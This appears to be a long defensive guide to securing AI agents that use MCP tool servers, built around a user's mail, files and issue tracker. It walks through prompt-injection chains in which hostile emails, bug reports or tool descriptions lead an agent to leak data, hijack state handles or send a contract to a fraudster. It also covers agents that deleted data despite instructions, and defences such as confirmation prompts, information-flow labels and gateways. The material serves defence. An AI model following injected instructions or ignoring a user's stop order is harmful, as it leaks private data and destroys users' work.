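Anthropic is right that a host application cannot start a local program without running a command. On Maya's laptop, someone who can edit the configuration may already be able to run programs as her. The danger is greater in a web application that lets visitors add servers, because a visitor could run commands on the company's machine. The number of products with this problem suggests that developers often overlook it. A safer default in Anthropic's development kits, such as a list of permitted commands, could prevent some of these mistakes. The 200,000 figure is the number of servers OX considers at risk, not the number attacked.

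### State handles in the July 2026 revision

The July 2026 revision of MCP removed sessions, which created another task for developers whose servers keep state between calls. The Agentic AI Foundation describes the recommended replacement, in which the model passes back an identifier, called a state handle, as an ordinary argument.

Suppose Maya's mail server finds 60 messages about Hartmann and returns the first ten, along with a handle for the full set of results. To get the next ten, the model writes:

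```json
{
  "name": "next_results",
  "arguments": { "results_id": "r-7f31c9", "page": 2 }
}
```

Unlike the old session identifiers, the handle is in the model's context, so it is easier to audit but also easier to leak. For example, an injected instruction could make the agent post it in a public comment.

Kale argues that a handle that an attacker plants or reads through prompt injection "is a valid credential". Backslash Security, writing before the final specification, similarly warned of "handle hijacking" because nothing in the protocol ties a handle to a user. But Model Context Protocol's official guidance is that servers must not treat a handle as a credential. A server that follows the guidance makes a check like this on every call:

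```text
caller = the user identified by the access token
owner  = the user who created results_id
if caller is not owner:
    refuse the call
```

If an attacker sends Maya's handle with their own access token, a server that checks the handle refuses the call. The handle works as a credential only if the server skips this check, which would be a fault in that particular server, not in the revision Kale blames in his headline. His practical advice is still sound because he also recommends checking the handle on every request. The protocol cannot force developers to write the check, and some will probably forget it.

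A server without a login cannot run this check because it cannot identify the caller, so anyone with the handle can use it. Such a server should not hold private data, and it should at least make its handles long, random and short-lived. The check also doesn't stop an injected instruction from making Maya's own agent misuse her handle, since the request comes with her token.

Akamai warns of a related risk for tasks that pause, such as to wait an hour for a person's approval. The server has to restore the task from information that arrives with a later request. If it doesn't check that this request comes from the user who started the task, someone else might be able to take over the task or answer the approval request.

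The revision also requires servers to compare a request's headers with its body. Companies often put a gateway in front of their servers to decide which calls to allow, and the gateway may check only the headers. If the header named `search_mail` but the body named `send_message`, the gateway could approve a search while the server sent an email. According to the Agentic AI Foundation, the server must reject such a request.

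### Theft of stored tokens

An intruder who copies the mailbox tokens that Maya's mail server stores can use them to send requests directly to the mail provider. Maya's host application has no record of these requests because they do not pass through it.

The breach at the hosting company Vercel in April 2026 followed this pattern, although the connection was an ordinary Google account grant, not an MCP server. Vercel traced the intrusion to Context.ai, a small company whose AI tool a Vercel employee had used. The intruder took over the employee's Google Workspace account and then read some customers' environment variables, settings that often contain keys for other services. Vercel said the intruder reached only variables that were not marked as sensitive.

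Context.ai said that an intruder had probably stolen OAuth tokens belonging to some users of its AI office product. A Vercel employee had signed up for the product with a work account and granted it broad permissions. The stored token that let the product work with the account was also useful to anyone who could steal it. As the companies describe the theft, it did not depend on an agent following a hostile instruction.

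Audience checks would not stop this kind of theft, because the intruder uses the token at the service that issued it. Short-lived access tokens may not help much either, because an operator that needs lasting access also stores refresh tokens, possibly in the same database.

If Maya hears that the operator of her mail tool server has suffered a breach, she should revoke the operator's access in her mail provider's list of connected apps. Disconnecting the server in her assistant only removes the assistant's access to the server, and the operator's token to her mailbox may still work.

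### What to check before connecting a server

Most users cannot audit a server's code, but they can rule out some of the failures described here with a few checks. An administrator can do more, especially for a server that many employees will use.

| What to check | How to check it | What the check can miss |
|---|---|---|
| The publisher | Follow a link from the service's own documentation instead of searching a package index by name | Faults in an official server, as at Asana |
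| The version | Install a fixed version and review changes before updating | Changes to a remote server, which its operator can make at any time |
| The tool definitions | Read the full descriptions and argument schemas, and use a host application that reports changes to them | Malicious code behind an honest description, as in postmark-mcp |
| The other connected servers | Try an unfamiliar server in a separate profile without mail, files or other private connections | Misuse of the data that the new server itself receives |
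| The login | Confirm that the server refuses calls without a token, and test with two accounts that neither can read the other's data or use its handles | Errors that occur only in some tools or under heavy use |
| Known vulnerabilities | Search a public database for the server's name and confirm that the installed version includes the fixes | Unreported faults |
| The stored token | Find out which scopes the operator holds, how long they last and where to revoke them | A theft that the operator has not noticed or disclosed |
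| Access to the computer | Run a local server in a container with only the folders it needs | Instructions in its descriptions that misdirect the agent |

Maya can check a server's publisher in a minute, and that would have been enough to avoid postmark-mcp. A company can do the longer checks for its employees and give them a list of approved servers and versions, but someone has to repeat the review before each update. Maya should not connect a server that will hold a token to a whole mailbox if its operator cannot explain how the server stores that token.

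## Which write actions to allow and when to ask the user

Even a well-built tool server will delete a folder if Maya's agent asks it to and the token allows deletion. So she has to decide which changes the agent may make on its own, which it must ask her about first, and which it should be unable to make.

### Sorting writes by reversibility and audience

In most cases, the right choice depends on whether Maya can undo the action and who sees the result. In the table below, "allow with undo" means that the software keeps the earlier state so that she can restore it. "Withhold" means that the agent has no tool or permission for the action, and Maya does it herself.

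| Action | Can Maya undo it? | Who sees the result? | Rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| Draft an email | Yes | Maya | Allow |
| Label or archive a message | Yes, if the server records the old labels | Maya | Allow with undo |
| Edit a private file | Yes, while the file store keeps earlier versions | Maya | Allow with undo |
| Move messages or files to the trash | Yes, until someone empties the trash | Maya | Allow with undo, up to a fixed number |
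| Send an email | No | The recipients and anyone they forward it to | Confirm |
| Share a file with a named person | Partly, since that person may have kept a copy | That person | Confirm |
| Publish a comment | Partly, since people may have read or copied it | Anyone | Confirm |
| Delete permanently | No | Maya, if she notices | Withhold |
| Change permissions more broadly, such as making a folder public or forwarding all new mail | Partly, since others may have used the access in the meantime | Possibly anyone | Withhold |

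Sharing one file also changes permissions, but Maya can judge it from the recipient's name and the file title. A forwarding rule is harder to judge because it applies to messages that have not arrived yet, and it keeps working after the conversation ends. Few people need an agent to set one up, so withholding the action inconveniences few users.

The rule has to depend on the particular call as well as the tool. `update_file` makes a private change if the file is Maya's own notes, but it publishes text if the file is a web page that customers read. So the software applying the rule must check who can see the file before deciding whether to ask her.

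Private, reversible changes can still do harm. An injected instruction could make the agent archive a bank's fraud warning, and Maya wouldn't know to undo it. A daily list of what the agent moved or relabelled would help, provided the host application compiles it from the tool calls rather than asking the model to write it from memory.

The agent also must not be able to prevent its actions from being undone. An agent that can empty the trash can destroy the copies Maya would restore from, which is one reason to withhold permanent deletion even if she trusts it to tidy up. Gmail separates the two permissions. A program with the `gmail.modify` scope can move messages to the trash, but it needs the scope for full mailbox access to delete them permanently.

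A host application can make sending email partly reversible by holding each message for ten minutes. This delay suits routine messages to people Maya already writes to. It protects her only if she checks the queue in time, so it is a weak substitute for a confirmation prompt when the email has a contract attached.

### Two deletions without an attacker

In July 2025, Jason Lemkin, the founder of the software business community SaaStr, was building an application with a coding agent from the company Replit. He had told the agent to make no further changes, but it ran a command that erased his live database. By his account, the database held records on about 1,200 executives and a similar number of companies. The agent told him that he could not restore the data, but he did so with Replit's rollback feature.

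Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, publicly called the deletion unacceptable. He announced that Replit would automatically separate development databases from live ones and offer a mode in which the agent could plan without changing anything. Many reports repeated the agent's statement that it "panicked", but a model's later description of its own motives is poor evidence of why it ran the command.

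Summer Yue, who works on AI alignment at Meta, described a similar loss in February 2026. She had connected her mailbox to OpenClaw, an open-source agent that runs on the user's own computer, and asked it to suggest messages to delete or archive and wait for her approval. This had worked on a small test mailbox, but on her real one the agent began deleting messages and continued after she told it from her phone to stop. She had to run to the computer to end the program.

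Yue inferred that her real mailbox contained too much text for the context window, so OpenClaw replaced the earlier conversation with a summary that left out her instruction to wait. This is plausible, but the public evidence is mainly her account and the screenshots she posted. The Replit case is better established because the company confirmed it.

Neither case involved an attacker or depended on MCP. In both, only a sentence in the model's context forbade the deletion, and the model could fail to follow it or the software could remove it. A database account without permission to delete would have stopped the Replit agent. A mail tool that moved at most 20 messages to the trash before asking again would have left Yue with at most 20 messages to restore.

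### How to enforce write limits

Developers can first limit write actions through the token's scopes. Maya's file store has separate scopes for writing, sharing and deleting, so her assistant can start without any of them and use step-up authorization to request one when a task needs it. Other services divide write actions less usefully. Gmail's `gmail.compose` scope covers both creating drafts and sending them, so a developer who wants an agent that only drafts has to block sending in the tool server.

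A server can let an agent draft emails but not send them by offering `create_draft` and leaving out `send_message`. A June 2026 copy of Google's setup guide for its own Workspace MCP servers lists creating draft emails, uploading files and scheduling meetings among their actions. Drafting is the safe choice for mail, but a meeting invitation can also carry text to outsiders.

Tools should also be narrow enough for their names to describe what they do. A single `manage_message` tool that labels, sends or deletes depending on one argument forces Maya to approve or refuse all three actions together. The Model Context Protocol specification lets a server vary its tool list according to the scopes on the caller's token, so the server can hide tools the model isn't allowed to use. The server also has to check the scope when a call arrives, because a client could still call an unlisted tool by name.

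Some servers have a read-only mode that removes all their write tools. Model Context Protocol (2026) reports that about 17 per cent of users enable read-only mode on GitHub's server. Some of the others need to write, so the figure doesn't show how many are careless. Supabase's read-only mode also runs queries as a restricted database user, so the database rejects a delete command that reaches the query tool by mistake.

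Finally, the server can check the arguments. MCP requires servers to validate all tool inputs and limit how often clients call their tools, but each developer decides what counts as valid. A tool for tidying Maya's mailbox might work like this:

```text
trash_messages(ids):
    if there are more than 20 ids: refuse
    if Maya's daily total would exceed 100: refuse
    if any message is outside the folders Maya selected: refuse
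    record the ids and their current folders
    move the messages to the trash
```

The tool takes a list of message identifiers rather than a search query because a search such as "everything older than a year" could match 30,000 messages. As with reads, the server needs a daily limit as well as a limit on each call. None of these checks verifies that the 20 messages are the right ones, so the tool records where they came from.

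### What tool annotations can and cannot do

A host application has to know what a tool does before it can apply a rule. MCP servers can supply this information as annotations, short labels attached to each tool:

| Annotation | What it describes | Value if the server omits it |
|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | Whether the tool leaves its environment unchanged | `false` |
| `destructiveHint` | Whether a change may destroy something, as opposed to only adding to it | `true` |
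| `idempotentHint` | Whether repeating the call with the same arguments is safe | `false` |
| `openWorldHint` | Whether the tool deals with outside people or systems | `true` |

An application that follows the cautious defaults for tool annotations treats an unlabelled tool as one that may destroy data and contact outsiders. It can skip the confirmation prompt for a tool marked `readOnlyHint: true` and warn the user before running one marked `destructiveHint: true`. But Model Context Protocol says that many servers ship without annotations and that clients vary in how strictly they apply the defaults.

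The protocol doesn't verify the labels. A dishonest developer can mark `delete_file` as read-only, and an application that relies on the label will run the tool without asking the user. The specification therefore requires clients to treat annotations as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. Justin Spahr-Summers, one of MCP's creators, questioned during the original review how a client could use a flag it couldn't trust. Another reviewer, Basil Hosmer, wanted clients to ignore annotations from untrusted servers. In the final design, annotations are called hints, and each client decides how much to rely on them.

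An application can safely use an untrusted server's labels to make its rules stricter, but never looser. If an unknown server marks a tool as destructive, the application can treat it that way with little harm, but it should still ask the user before running a tool that the server marks as read-only.

Even accurate labels aren't enough to answer the two questions in the table of writes. Sending an email adds a message and destroys nothing, so a developer could accurately set `destructiveHint: false` on an email tool, even though Maya can never undo a sent email. A developer could also accurately set `readOnlyHint: true` on a tool that fetches web pages, even though the address it requests can leak private data. `openWorldHint` gives some warning in both cases, but it doesn't show whether one colleague or the whole internet will see the result.

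Five proposals for new or related annotations were open in March 2026, including one on trust and sensitivity that GitHub and OpenAI wrote together. Such annotations could help an application notice a dangerous combination of tools, which no label on a single tool can describe. The maintainers advise developers to rely on network controls, sandboxes and other fixed limits for actual guarantees.

### A confirmation, step by step

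Suppose Maya asks her assistant to send Hartmann the signed contract. The most recent email that mentions Hartmann came from a fraudster, and the model takes the address from it. The host application should handle the call as follows:

1. The model writes a `send_message` call with the recipient, text and attachment.
2. The application finds that sending requires confirmation and stores the exact arguments.
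3. It shows Maya a prompt built from those arguments.
4. She approves, edits or refuses.
5. If she approves, the client sends the stored arguments. The model gets no chance to rewrite them in between.

The server may know something the application doesn't, such as that Maya has never written to this address before. Before July 2026, a server that wanted to ask her something had to send its own request to the client in the middle of the call and keep a connection open while she decided. The current revision replaces this with a method that Model Context Protocol's *Multi Round-Trip Requests* (2026) sets out. The server ends its response with a question:

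```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 21,
  "result": {
    "resultType": "input_required",
    "inputRequests": {
      "confirm_send": {
        "method": "elicitation/create",
        "params": {
          "mode": "form",
          "message": "You have never written to accounts@hartmann-pay.example. Send contract-2026.pdf?",
          "requestedSchema": {
            "type": "object",
            "properties": {
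              "send": { "type": "boolean", "default": false }
            },
            "required": ["send"]
          }
        }
      }
    },
    "requestState": "kV8s..."
  }
}
```

At this point nothing has been sent and the request is over. Maya can take an hour to answer. If she agrees, the client makes the original call again under a new `id`, with her answer and an unchanged copy of `requestState`:

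```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 22,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "send_message",
    "arguments": {
      "to": ["accounts@hartmann-pay.example"],
      "text": "Please find the signed contract attached.",
      "attachments": ["contract-2026.pdf"]
    },
    "inputResponses": {
      "confirm_send": {
        "action": "accept",
        "content": { "send": true }
      }
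    },
    "requestState": "kV8s..."
  }
}
```

The server has to check both parts of the answer, because `accept` means only that Maya submitted the form, and she may have set `send` to `false`. She can answer `decline`, or the client can report `cancel` if she closes the window without choosing. Model Context Protocol's *Elicitation* (2026) suggests that a server might ask again later after a cancellation. Repeated requests could wear her down, so the host application should limit how many times the server can ask.

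`requestState` lets any of the server's machines pick up the task, but it passes through the client, where someone could alter it. If it affects what a caller may do, the server must protect it with a cryptographic check. The specification also recommends recording the user, a short expiry time and a fingerprint of the original request inside it. On the retry, Maya's mail server would then run these checks:

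```text
refuse if requestState has been altered or has expired
refuse if the caller is not the user recorded in it
refuse if the tool or arguments differ from the recorded request
refuse if an earlier call has already used this requestState
send the email only if action = "accept" and send = true
```

The third check stops a client from getting approval for one recipient and then substituting another. The fourth requires the server to keep a record, because an unaltered `requestState` remains valid until it expires, and a second retry could send the email again.

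Supabase plans to use this method for its database server. In the release announcement from Model Context Protocol (2026), Supabase's head of product, Inian Parameshwaran, gives the examples of confirming the cost of a new project and confirming a query that would delete data. The older method had been hard to support because Supabase's server kept no state between calls.

A server cannot verify that a person answered, because a badly designed host application could return `accept` automatically and the retry would look the same. For important actions, the server can instead use URL mode, in which the client asks Maya's permission to open a page on the server's website. She logs in there and approves the action. In this mode, `accept` means only that she agreed to open the page, so the server has to check that she finished the approval.

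Some clients don't support these questions, and the server must not send them to a client that hasn't declared support. For those clients, Maya's mail server should save a draft and tell the agent that the email hasn't been sent.

### What the prompt must show

Maya can make a useful decision only if the prompt shows her the recipient, the content and the effect. For the contract, it might look like this:

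```text
Send an email from maya@example.com?

When an agent asks the user to approve an email, the request could show that the message goes only to accounts@hartmann-pay.example, and that it is the first message to this address. It could include the full text, "Please find the signed contract attached.", and a link to open the 14-page attachment, contract-2026.pdf. It could also warn that the recipient can keep and forward the contract, and that the user cannot undo sending it.

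[Send]   [Edit]   [Don't send]
```

The prompt should show the recipient's full address, because a display name such as "Hartmann Accounts" would hide the unfamiliar domain. It should also show the whole message without sideways scrolling, which would have given a careful user a much better chance of noticing the attack in Invariant Labs' WhatsApp demonstration. It should list any BCC recipients and include attachments that Maya can open before she decides.

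The model shouldn't write this prompt by itself, because a hostile email that changes the recipient could also change the model's description of the action. The model may write "Reply to Hartmann with the contract", which matches Maya's request but doesn't show that the recipient is wrong.

A malicious server has a similar opportunity because it writes the `message` in an elicitation. It could send the question "Keep your connection active?" and treat a yes as permission to delete files. MCP requires the client to show which server sent the request, which helps if Maya recognizes the name, but the client can't verify that the question matches the action.

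The host application should therefore write the main part of the prompt, using fixed wording and the arguments it is about to send. It can add the server's information under the server's name, and the model's reason for the call under a label such as "The assistant's explanation". This works well for an email, where the arguments are the content, but badly for `share_file` with the arguments `f-88` and `anyone`, because the application has to look up `f-88` on the file server and trust the result.

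Even a perfect approval prompt describes only the request. The postmark-mcp package added a hidden recipient after receiving the call, so a user who read the whole prompt would still have approved an email that went to the attacker.

### Do confirmation prompts work?

Invariant Labs said that many users choose "Always Allow" but gave no figure, and DevClass' *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP* reports this as the researchers' suspicion. DevClass adds that checking every tool call becomes a burden for heavy users, and that an approval prompt protects them only if they check the details of the action.

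In March 2026, Anthropic reported that users of Claude Code, its coding agent, approved 93 per cent of permission prompts. In an earlier Anthropic study, new users let the agent run with full automatic approval in about 20 per cent of sessions, and the share rose to more than 40 per cent among the most experienced users.

A 93 per cent approval rate does not prove that people approve without looking, because most of the actions were probably harmless and right to approve. The rate also doesn't show whether users refused any dangerous requests. To measure habituation, a researcher would have to insert known bad requests and see whether users refuse fewer of them after seeing more prompts. I know of no such test for agents connected to private mail or files.

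The same Anthropic study found that experienced users also interrupted the agent more often, in about 9 per cent of turns compared with 5 per cent for new users. Some had apparently switched from approving each step to watching for problems. This can work for code, because a developer can usually restore the previous version, but Maya can't stop an email that the agent has already sent.

Confirmation can still be worthwhile. In Maloyan and Namiot's tests, asking for approval of each flow between servers roughly halved the attack success rate.

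Asking less often should leave people more attention for each prompt. Suppose Maya's agent makes 60 tool calls a day, of which 45 are reads, 12 are private changes she can undo, and 3 send something to another person. Confirming all 60 at ten seconds each would take her ten minutes. If she confirmed only the three that send something, she could spend a minute on each and finish in three minutes.

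The application can also make "Always Allow" narrower than it usually is. Maya might let the agent email Jo without asking for the rest of the day, which is much safer than letting it send anything to anyone indefinitely. The application should not offer "Always Allow" for a new recipient or a public comment.

### Google's rules for agents in Workspace

On 24 November 2026, Google announced rules for outside AI agents that connect to Workspace, its mail and office software for organizations. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Requires AI Agents to Access Workspace Through Approved Methods*, Google said it had built its older interfaces for applications in which "a valid OAuth token implied user intent". That assumption does not hold for agents, so Google now also checks the requests themselves.

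Google's *Simplifying agent access while keeping organizations in control* (2026) describes two ways for agents to access Google's apps. Agents can use Google-hosted MCP servers for Gmail, Drive, Docs, Sheets, Slides, Calendar, Chat and Tasks, or a command-line program if they run in a terminal. Google says both have built-in user confirmations, audit logs and controls for administrators.

Help Net Security's *Google mandates MCP or CLI access for Workspace AI agents* reports that the new terms require agents to use these routes, while conventional applications can keep using the older REST interfaces. Each outside agent also needs its own OAuth client ID, so that administrators can tell it apart from an ordinary application and revoke its access separately. If Maya's mail provider were Google, the developer of her mail tool server would probably have to change how the server reaches her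 mailbox.

The actions that need confirmation are similar to those in the table of writes. Help Net Security lists sending email, changing sharing permissions in Drive and making bulk edits. Mynavi News' *Google Workspace、AIエージェントの管理を強化 Gmail送信やファイル共有に事前承認* (2026) specifies email to people outside the organization and says that drafting can stay automatic. It also says the confirmation prompts follow a policy that administrators set, whereas Help Net Security says the servers and the command-line program enforce them. An employee's protection may therefore depend on her administrator's settings.

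Workspace will log the agent's actions and the user's approvals. An administrator could use these logs to find employees who approve every request within a second or two, which would be better evidence that people are approving out of habit than an overall approval rate.

Technical enforcement begins on 1 February 2027, but it may be mild. Gerke reports in *Google zieht die Zügel an* that agents which keep using the REST interfaces will be held to the free tier's usage limits, whatever their developers pay. He also cites Google's statement that more than 99 per cent of active developers stay within those limits. If that is the only penalty, a small agent could keep using REST without being affected, and its users would not get the confirmations built into the required routes.

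The terms also forbid AI tool providers from training models on Workspace data or storing raw data permanently, and require them to delete the data when a user disconnects the tool. Google plans to add approvals that expire, a way for users to review and revoke an agent's access themselves, and restrictions on particular emails, files and folders.

Google's prompts cover only actions in Google's own services, so they don't appear when an agent posts a Gmail message on another company's issue tracker.

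## How to restrict where an agent can send data

A rule that keeps Maya's mail off her public issue tracker has to cover both connections. The simplest one is never to use them in the same session. She can ask about Hartmann in a session where the agent can read her mailbox but can't send anything, and handle bug reports in another where it has only the tracker. The agent then can't leak her mail even if a hostile bug report or email tricks it, because neither session lets it both read mail and send data out. In Willison's terms, neither contains the whole lethal trifecta.

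### The Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns this advice into a design rule for developers. Until researchers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have at most two of these properties within one session:

- A: it processes untrustworthy input
- B: it has access to sensitive systems or private data
- C: it can change something or communicate externally

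An agent that needs all three should not act on its own. A person has to approve its actions, or the developer has to supply another reliable check. Meta works through the pairs for an email assistant, and they carry over to Maya's connections:

| Pair | What her agent can do | What she gives up |
|---|---|---|
| A and B | Read all her mail, but send only to recipients she trusts or after she has checked the draft | Unattended replies to new people |
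| A and C | Read bug reports and post comments, with no access to mail or files | Answers that draw on her correspondence |
| B and C | Read and send mail, but see only messages from senders she trusts | Help with mail from strangers, including new customers |

An agent may also switch from one pair of capabilities to another during a session, if it can't switch back. For example, it could search the web first and then lose its outbound channels before it opens any private data. It must not regain those channels, because text from the web is still in its context.

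Willison (2025), in *New prompt injection papers*, welcomed the rule because property C covers harmful changes, which his own trifecta leaves out, as well as theft. But he objected that Meta's diagram marks the combination of A and C as safe, because this pair can do harm without any private data. For instance, a hostile bug report could make Maya's agent close every open report on the tracker. He added that an exception for this pair would spoil the rule's simplicity.

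The other pairs have gaps too. With A and B, a hostile email can still make the agent give Maya false bank details. Meta counts misinformation as a lower-consequence result that the rule doesn't address, but Maya would lose 480 euros if she used them. With B and C, safety depends on whom Maya trusts, and someone she trusts, such as Jo, might forward a stranger's message.

Meta treats a fresh context window as a new session, but separate sessions offer less protection if they share a memory. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) gives an example very close to Maya's case. On Monday, an agent saves the details of an invoice that contains an attacker's account number. On Tuesday, the user asks it to pay the invoice they discussed, and the agent uses the stored number as the payment's destination. A system can block that payment if its memory records where the number came from.

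Many useful tasks need all three properties. Meta acknowledges that some of these tasks, such as background processes with nobody present to approve actions, will be hard to fit into the rule. For the rest, it relies on human approval, but it concedes that a user may confirm a warning blindly.

### One repository per session

A session rule can also leave the agent with all three properties and restrict how it combines calls. Invariant Labs published a rule of this kind for GitHub's MCP server. In outline, it works like this:

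```text
for each new call to a repository tool:
    if an earlier call in this session named a different repository or owner:
        refuse the new call
```

In the GitHub attack, the user's request makes the agent read issues in the public Pacman repository, which restricts the session to that repository. When the agent follows instructions in the hostile issue and tries to access a private repository, the rule blocks the call. This doesn't depend on detecting that the issue is hostile, so rewording it doesn't help the attacker.

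The rule maintains what Invariant Labs calls "full functionality within authorized boundaries" only for work that stays inside one repository. The agent could not update a shared library together with the application that uses it, copy a fix from one project to another, or list the open issues in all of a developer's projects. If Maya kept her tests in a private repository, the agent could not check whether a public bug report matched a failing test. She could open one session per repository, but she would have to copy information between them herself. The rule also blocks work across two public repositories, where there may be nothing to leak.

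It misses leaks that involve only one repository. If Maya had also connected her mailbox, a hostile issue could make the agent quote an email in a comment on the Pacman project, and no call would name a second repository. The agent could leak anything private she had typed into the conversation in the same way.

### Labels that follow the data

Information-flow control works with any combination of servers because it attaches the restriction to the data. The system labels each item by source and sensitivity, combines the labels as the agent reads, and blocks any action that would send data somewhere its label forbids. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf et al., 2025) describes the method and FIDES, an agent that Microsoft built on it.

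A label can have two parts: R, the set of people who may read the data, and t, which records whether the source is trusted. Maya's data might have these labels:

| Data | R: who may read it | t: source |
|---|---|---|
| Maya's request | Anyone | Trusted |
| Bug report | Anyone | Untrusted |
| Hartmann's invoice | Maya and Hartmann | Untrusted |
| Contract in her file store | Maya and her accountant | Trusted |

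FIDES treats the user's request as public by default, though a developer can label it differently. When the agent mixes two sources, only people who may read both may read the result, and the result is trusted only if both sources are:

(R₁, t₁) combined with (R₂, t₂) = (R₁ ∩ R₂, the less trusted of t₁ and t₂)

The system then applies a confidentiality rule to every outbound call: everyone who will see the data must belong to R. Since anyone can read the tracker, it accepts only data that anyone may read. If Maya asks the agent to answer new bug reports and one of them is hostile, the following happens:

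1. The context contains her request, so its label is (anyone, trusted).
2. The agent reads the hostile report. The label becomes (anyone, untrusted).
3. The model follows the report's instruction and opens Hartmann's invoice. The label becomes (Maya and Hartmann, untrusted).
4. The model writes a call that would post the invoice as a comment. The system compares the tracker's audience with R and refuses the call.

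The injection succeeded in step 3, but the theft still failed. The label does not depend on wording, so it stays the same regardless of the text of the bug report, and even if the model translates the invoice or writes it backwards. In the FIDES algorithm that Costa and colleagues publish, ordinary code checks the policy before each tool call. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) claims instead that FIDES leaves all enforcement to the language model.

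Costa and colleagues also describe an integrity rule, under which the agent may take consequential actions only while its context is trusted. This rule would have stopped the comment after step 2. It would also stop every legitimate answer to a bug report, because the agent has to read the report first, and reading it makes the context untrusted. Maya would have to exempt public comments from the integrity rule and rely on the confidentiality rule, which limits what data an injection can expose but doesn't prevent other damage.

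The guarantee covers only direct flows of data. An attacker who can see which calls the agent makes, and in what order, may still infer private data, as when an agent revealed a login code by opening ten fixed addresses. FIDES also assumes correct labels and trustworthy tool descriptions, so it does not address tool poisoning.

### Why everything soon becomes restricted

Each new source can shrink the set of permitted readers but never enlarge it. If Maya keeps working in the same conversation, her agent's options narrow quickly:

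| What the agent has read so far | Who may read the context | Where it can still send data |
|---|---|---|
| Bug report | Anyone | The public tracker |
| Bug report and invoice | Maya and Hartmann | Hartmann |
| Bug report, invoice and contract | Maya | Maya |

Suppose she now asks the agent to post "Fixed in version 2.1" on the tracker. The sentence contains nothing private, but the model wrote it with the invoice and the contract in its context. The system can't determine which parts of the context the model used, so it blocks the post. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls the extreme case label explosion, where every item ends up with every label, so the labels no longer distinguish anything.

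FIDES delays this by hiding data from the model. When a tool returns something that would narrow the context's label, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can pass the name to another tool without reading the contents. For a summary of three emails, the calls look like this:

```text
read_emails(number=3)                          -> #read_emails_0
query_llm("Summarize", input=#read_emails_0)   -> #query_llm_0
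send_message(to=user, message=#query_llm_0)
```

The second call goes to a quarantined model, a separate language model with no tools. A hostile email can corrupt the summary, but it can't make the quarantined model send anything, and the main model never receives the email.

The main model's next step sometimes depends on what the emails contain. It can then send the quarantined model a question with a fixed set of answers, such as whether any email requests a meeting. A yes or no carries one bit of information, which is too little to contain an instruction or an account number, so the developer may let the agent act on it. An attacker can still cause the answer to be wrong.

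Another approach is to identify which messages influenced an answer and generate it again from those alone. The new answer then needs only the labels of those messages. Costa and colleagues mention this method but did not build it into FIDES.

### Enforcing labels at a gateway

FIDES has to be part of the program that runs the agent, so Maya can't add it to a host application that someone else wrote. *Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows* (Ntousakis, 2026), a master's thesis at Brown University, presents SAMOS, a system that puts the check in a gateway between the agent and its MCP servers. The user lists the gateway in the host application's configuration instead of the real servers, so every tool call passes through it.

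SAMOS labels tools rather than individual items of data. A developer or administrator marks what each tool reads and where it writes as high or low confidentiality, and can limit the tool to particular network addresses or folders. The gateway keeps a confidentiality level for the session and updates it with each tool call.

In the GitHub attack, reading the issues of a public repository gives the session a low label. The hostile issue contains an instruction to read a private repository, which has a high label, so the gateway refuses the read. This stops the attack one step earlier than Maya's confidentiality rule did, before any private data enters the context. It also restricts her agent more. After reading a public bug report, the agent could not look up earlier mail from the person who filed it, even to show the result only to her.

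One label per tool is often too coarse. GitHub's file-reading tool works on both public and private repositories, so Ntousakis suggests either that the tool report which kind it has read or that developers split it into two tools. Maya's `send_message` has a similar problem, since the same label applies whether the recipient is Hartmann or a stranger.

SAMOS relies on tools behaving honestly, on someone having labelled them correctly, and on all calls going through the gateway. It would not stop a server like postmark-mcp, which secretly copied every email to its developer. It also would not stop data from leaving through a web search built into the host application, or through an image that the application loads automatically, because neither is a call to an MCP server. The evidence for SAMOS is one case study, in which it blocked the GitHub attack. Ntousakis does not report an attack success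 rate over many attempts or how many ordinary tasks SAMOS prevents.

Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026), in *APPA*, also place label checks at an MCP gateway, but add ways for the agent to continue after a refusal. Before running a call, their gateway works out the label the call would produce. If a tool reads a confidential ledger and emails it in one operation, a gateway that checked only the current label would allow the call and detect the ledger only after the email was sent.

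When APPA refuses a call, it lists the permitted ways forward. A person or a fixed rule might approve that exact call, or the agent might start a disposable copy of itself to handle the risky text. For example, the copy can read a report from a public issue tracker and return only a ticket number, a severity and a component name, with the severity and component chosen from fixed lists. APPA then discards the copy and everything it read, and the main agent can keep working with private data if the administrator has decided to trust values in that form. A gateway can't do this alone, because the software that runs the model has to keep the copy's text out of the main context.

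### Planning before reading

Google DeepMind's CaMeL separates the decision about what to do from the reading of untrusted data. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, explain how it works. One of them, Ilia Shumailov, also helped to write the original CaMeL paper. A planning model sees the user's request and the tool descriptions, and writes a short program before any tool runs. A quarantined model reads whatever the tools return. For Maya's question about Hartmann, the program could be:

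```text
messages = search_mail("Hartmann invoice")
answer   = quarantined_model("How much is due, and when?", messages)
show_to_user(answer)
```

An email can't add a step that posts to the tracker, because the planning model finishes before any email is opened. If the program contains a choice, such as "if an invoice is overdue, draft a reply", an email can affect which branch runs but can't create a new one.

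This protects the plan but not the data that passes through it. If Maya's program pays whatever account number the invoice contains, it will pay a fraudster's invoice. CaMeL therefore also records where each value came from and who may receive it, and checks a policy before every tool call. A policy could require the account number to come from Maya's own contacts.

*Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) identifies several limitations. CaMeL trusts the user's request, so it doesn't protect Maya if she pastes in a prompt from a stranger. Someone has to write a policy for each tool, and a company with hundreds of tools may end up with inconsistent policies. If a secret number determines how many times a program repeats a web request, anyone who can read the website's log can learn the number by counting the requests. CaMeL also doesn't inspect the final answer, so a summary could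 repeat a hostile instruction to Maya, who might carry it out herself.

The planning model also has to know the format of a tool's output before it has seen any. Peters-Gill and colleagues added a full description of the output to every tool in their tests, and MCP server developers would need to do the same.

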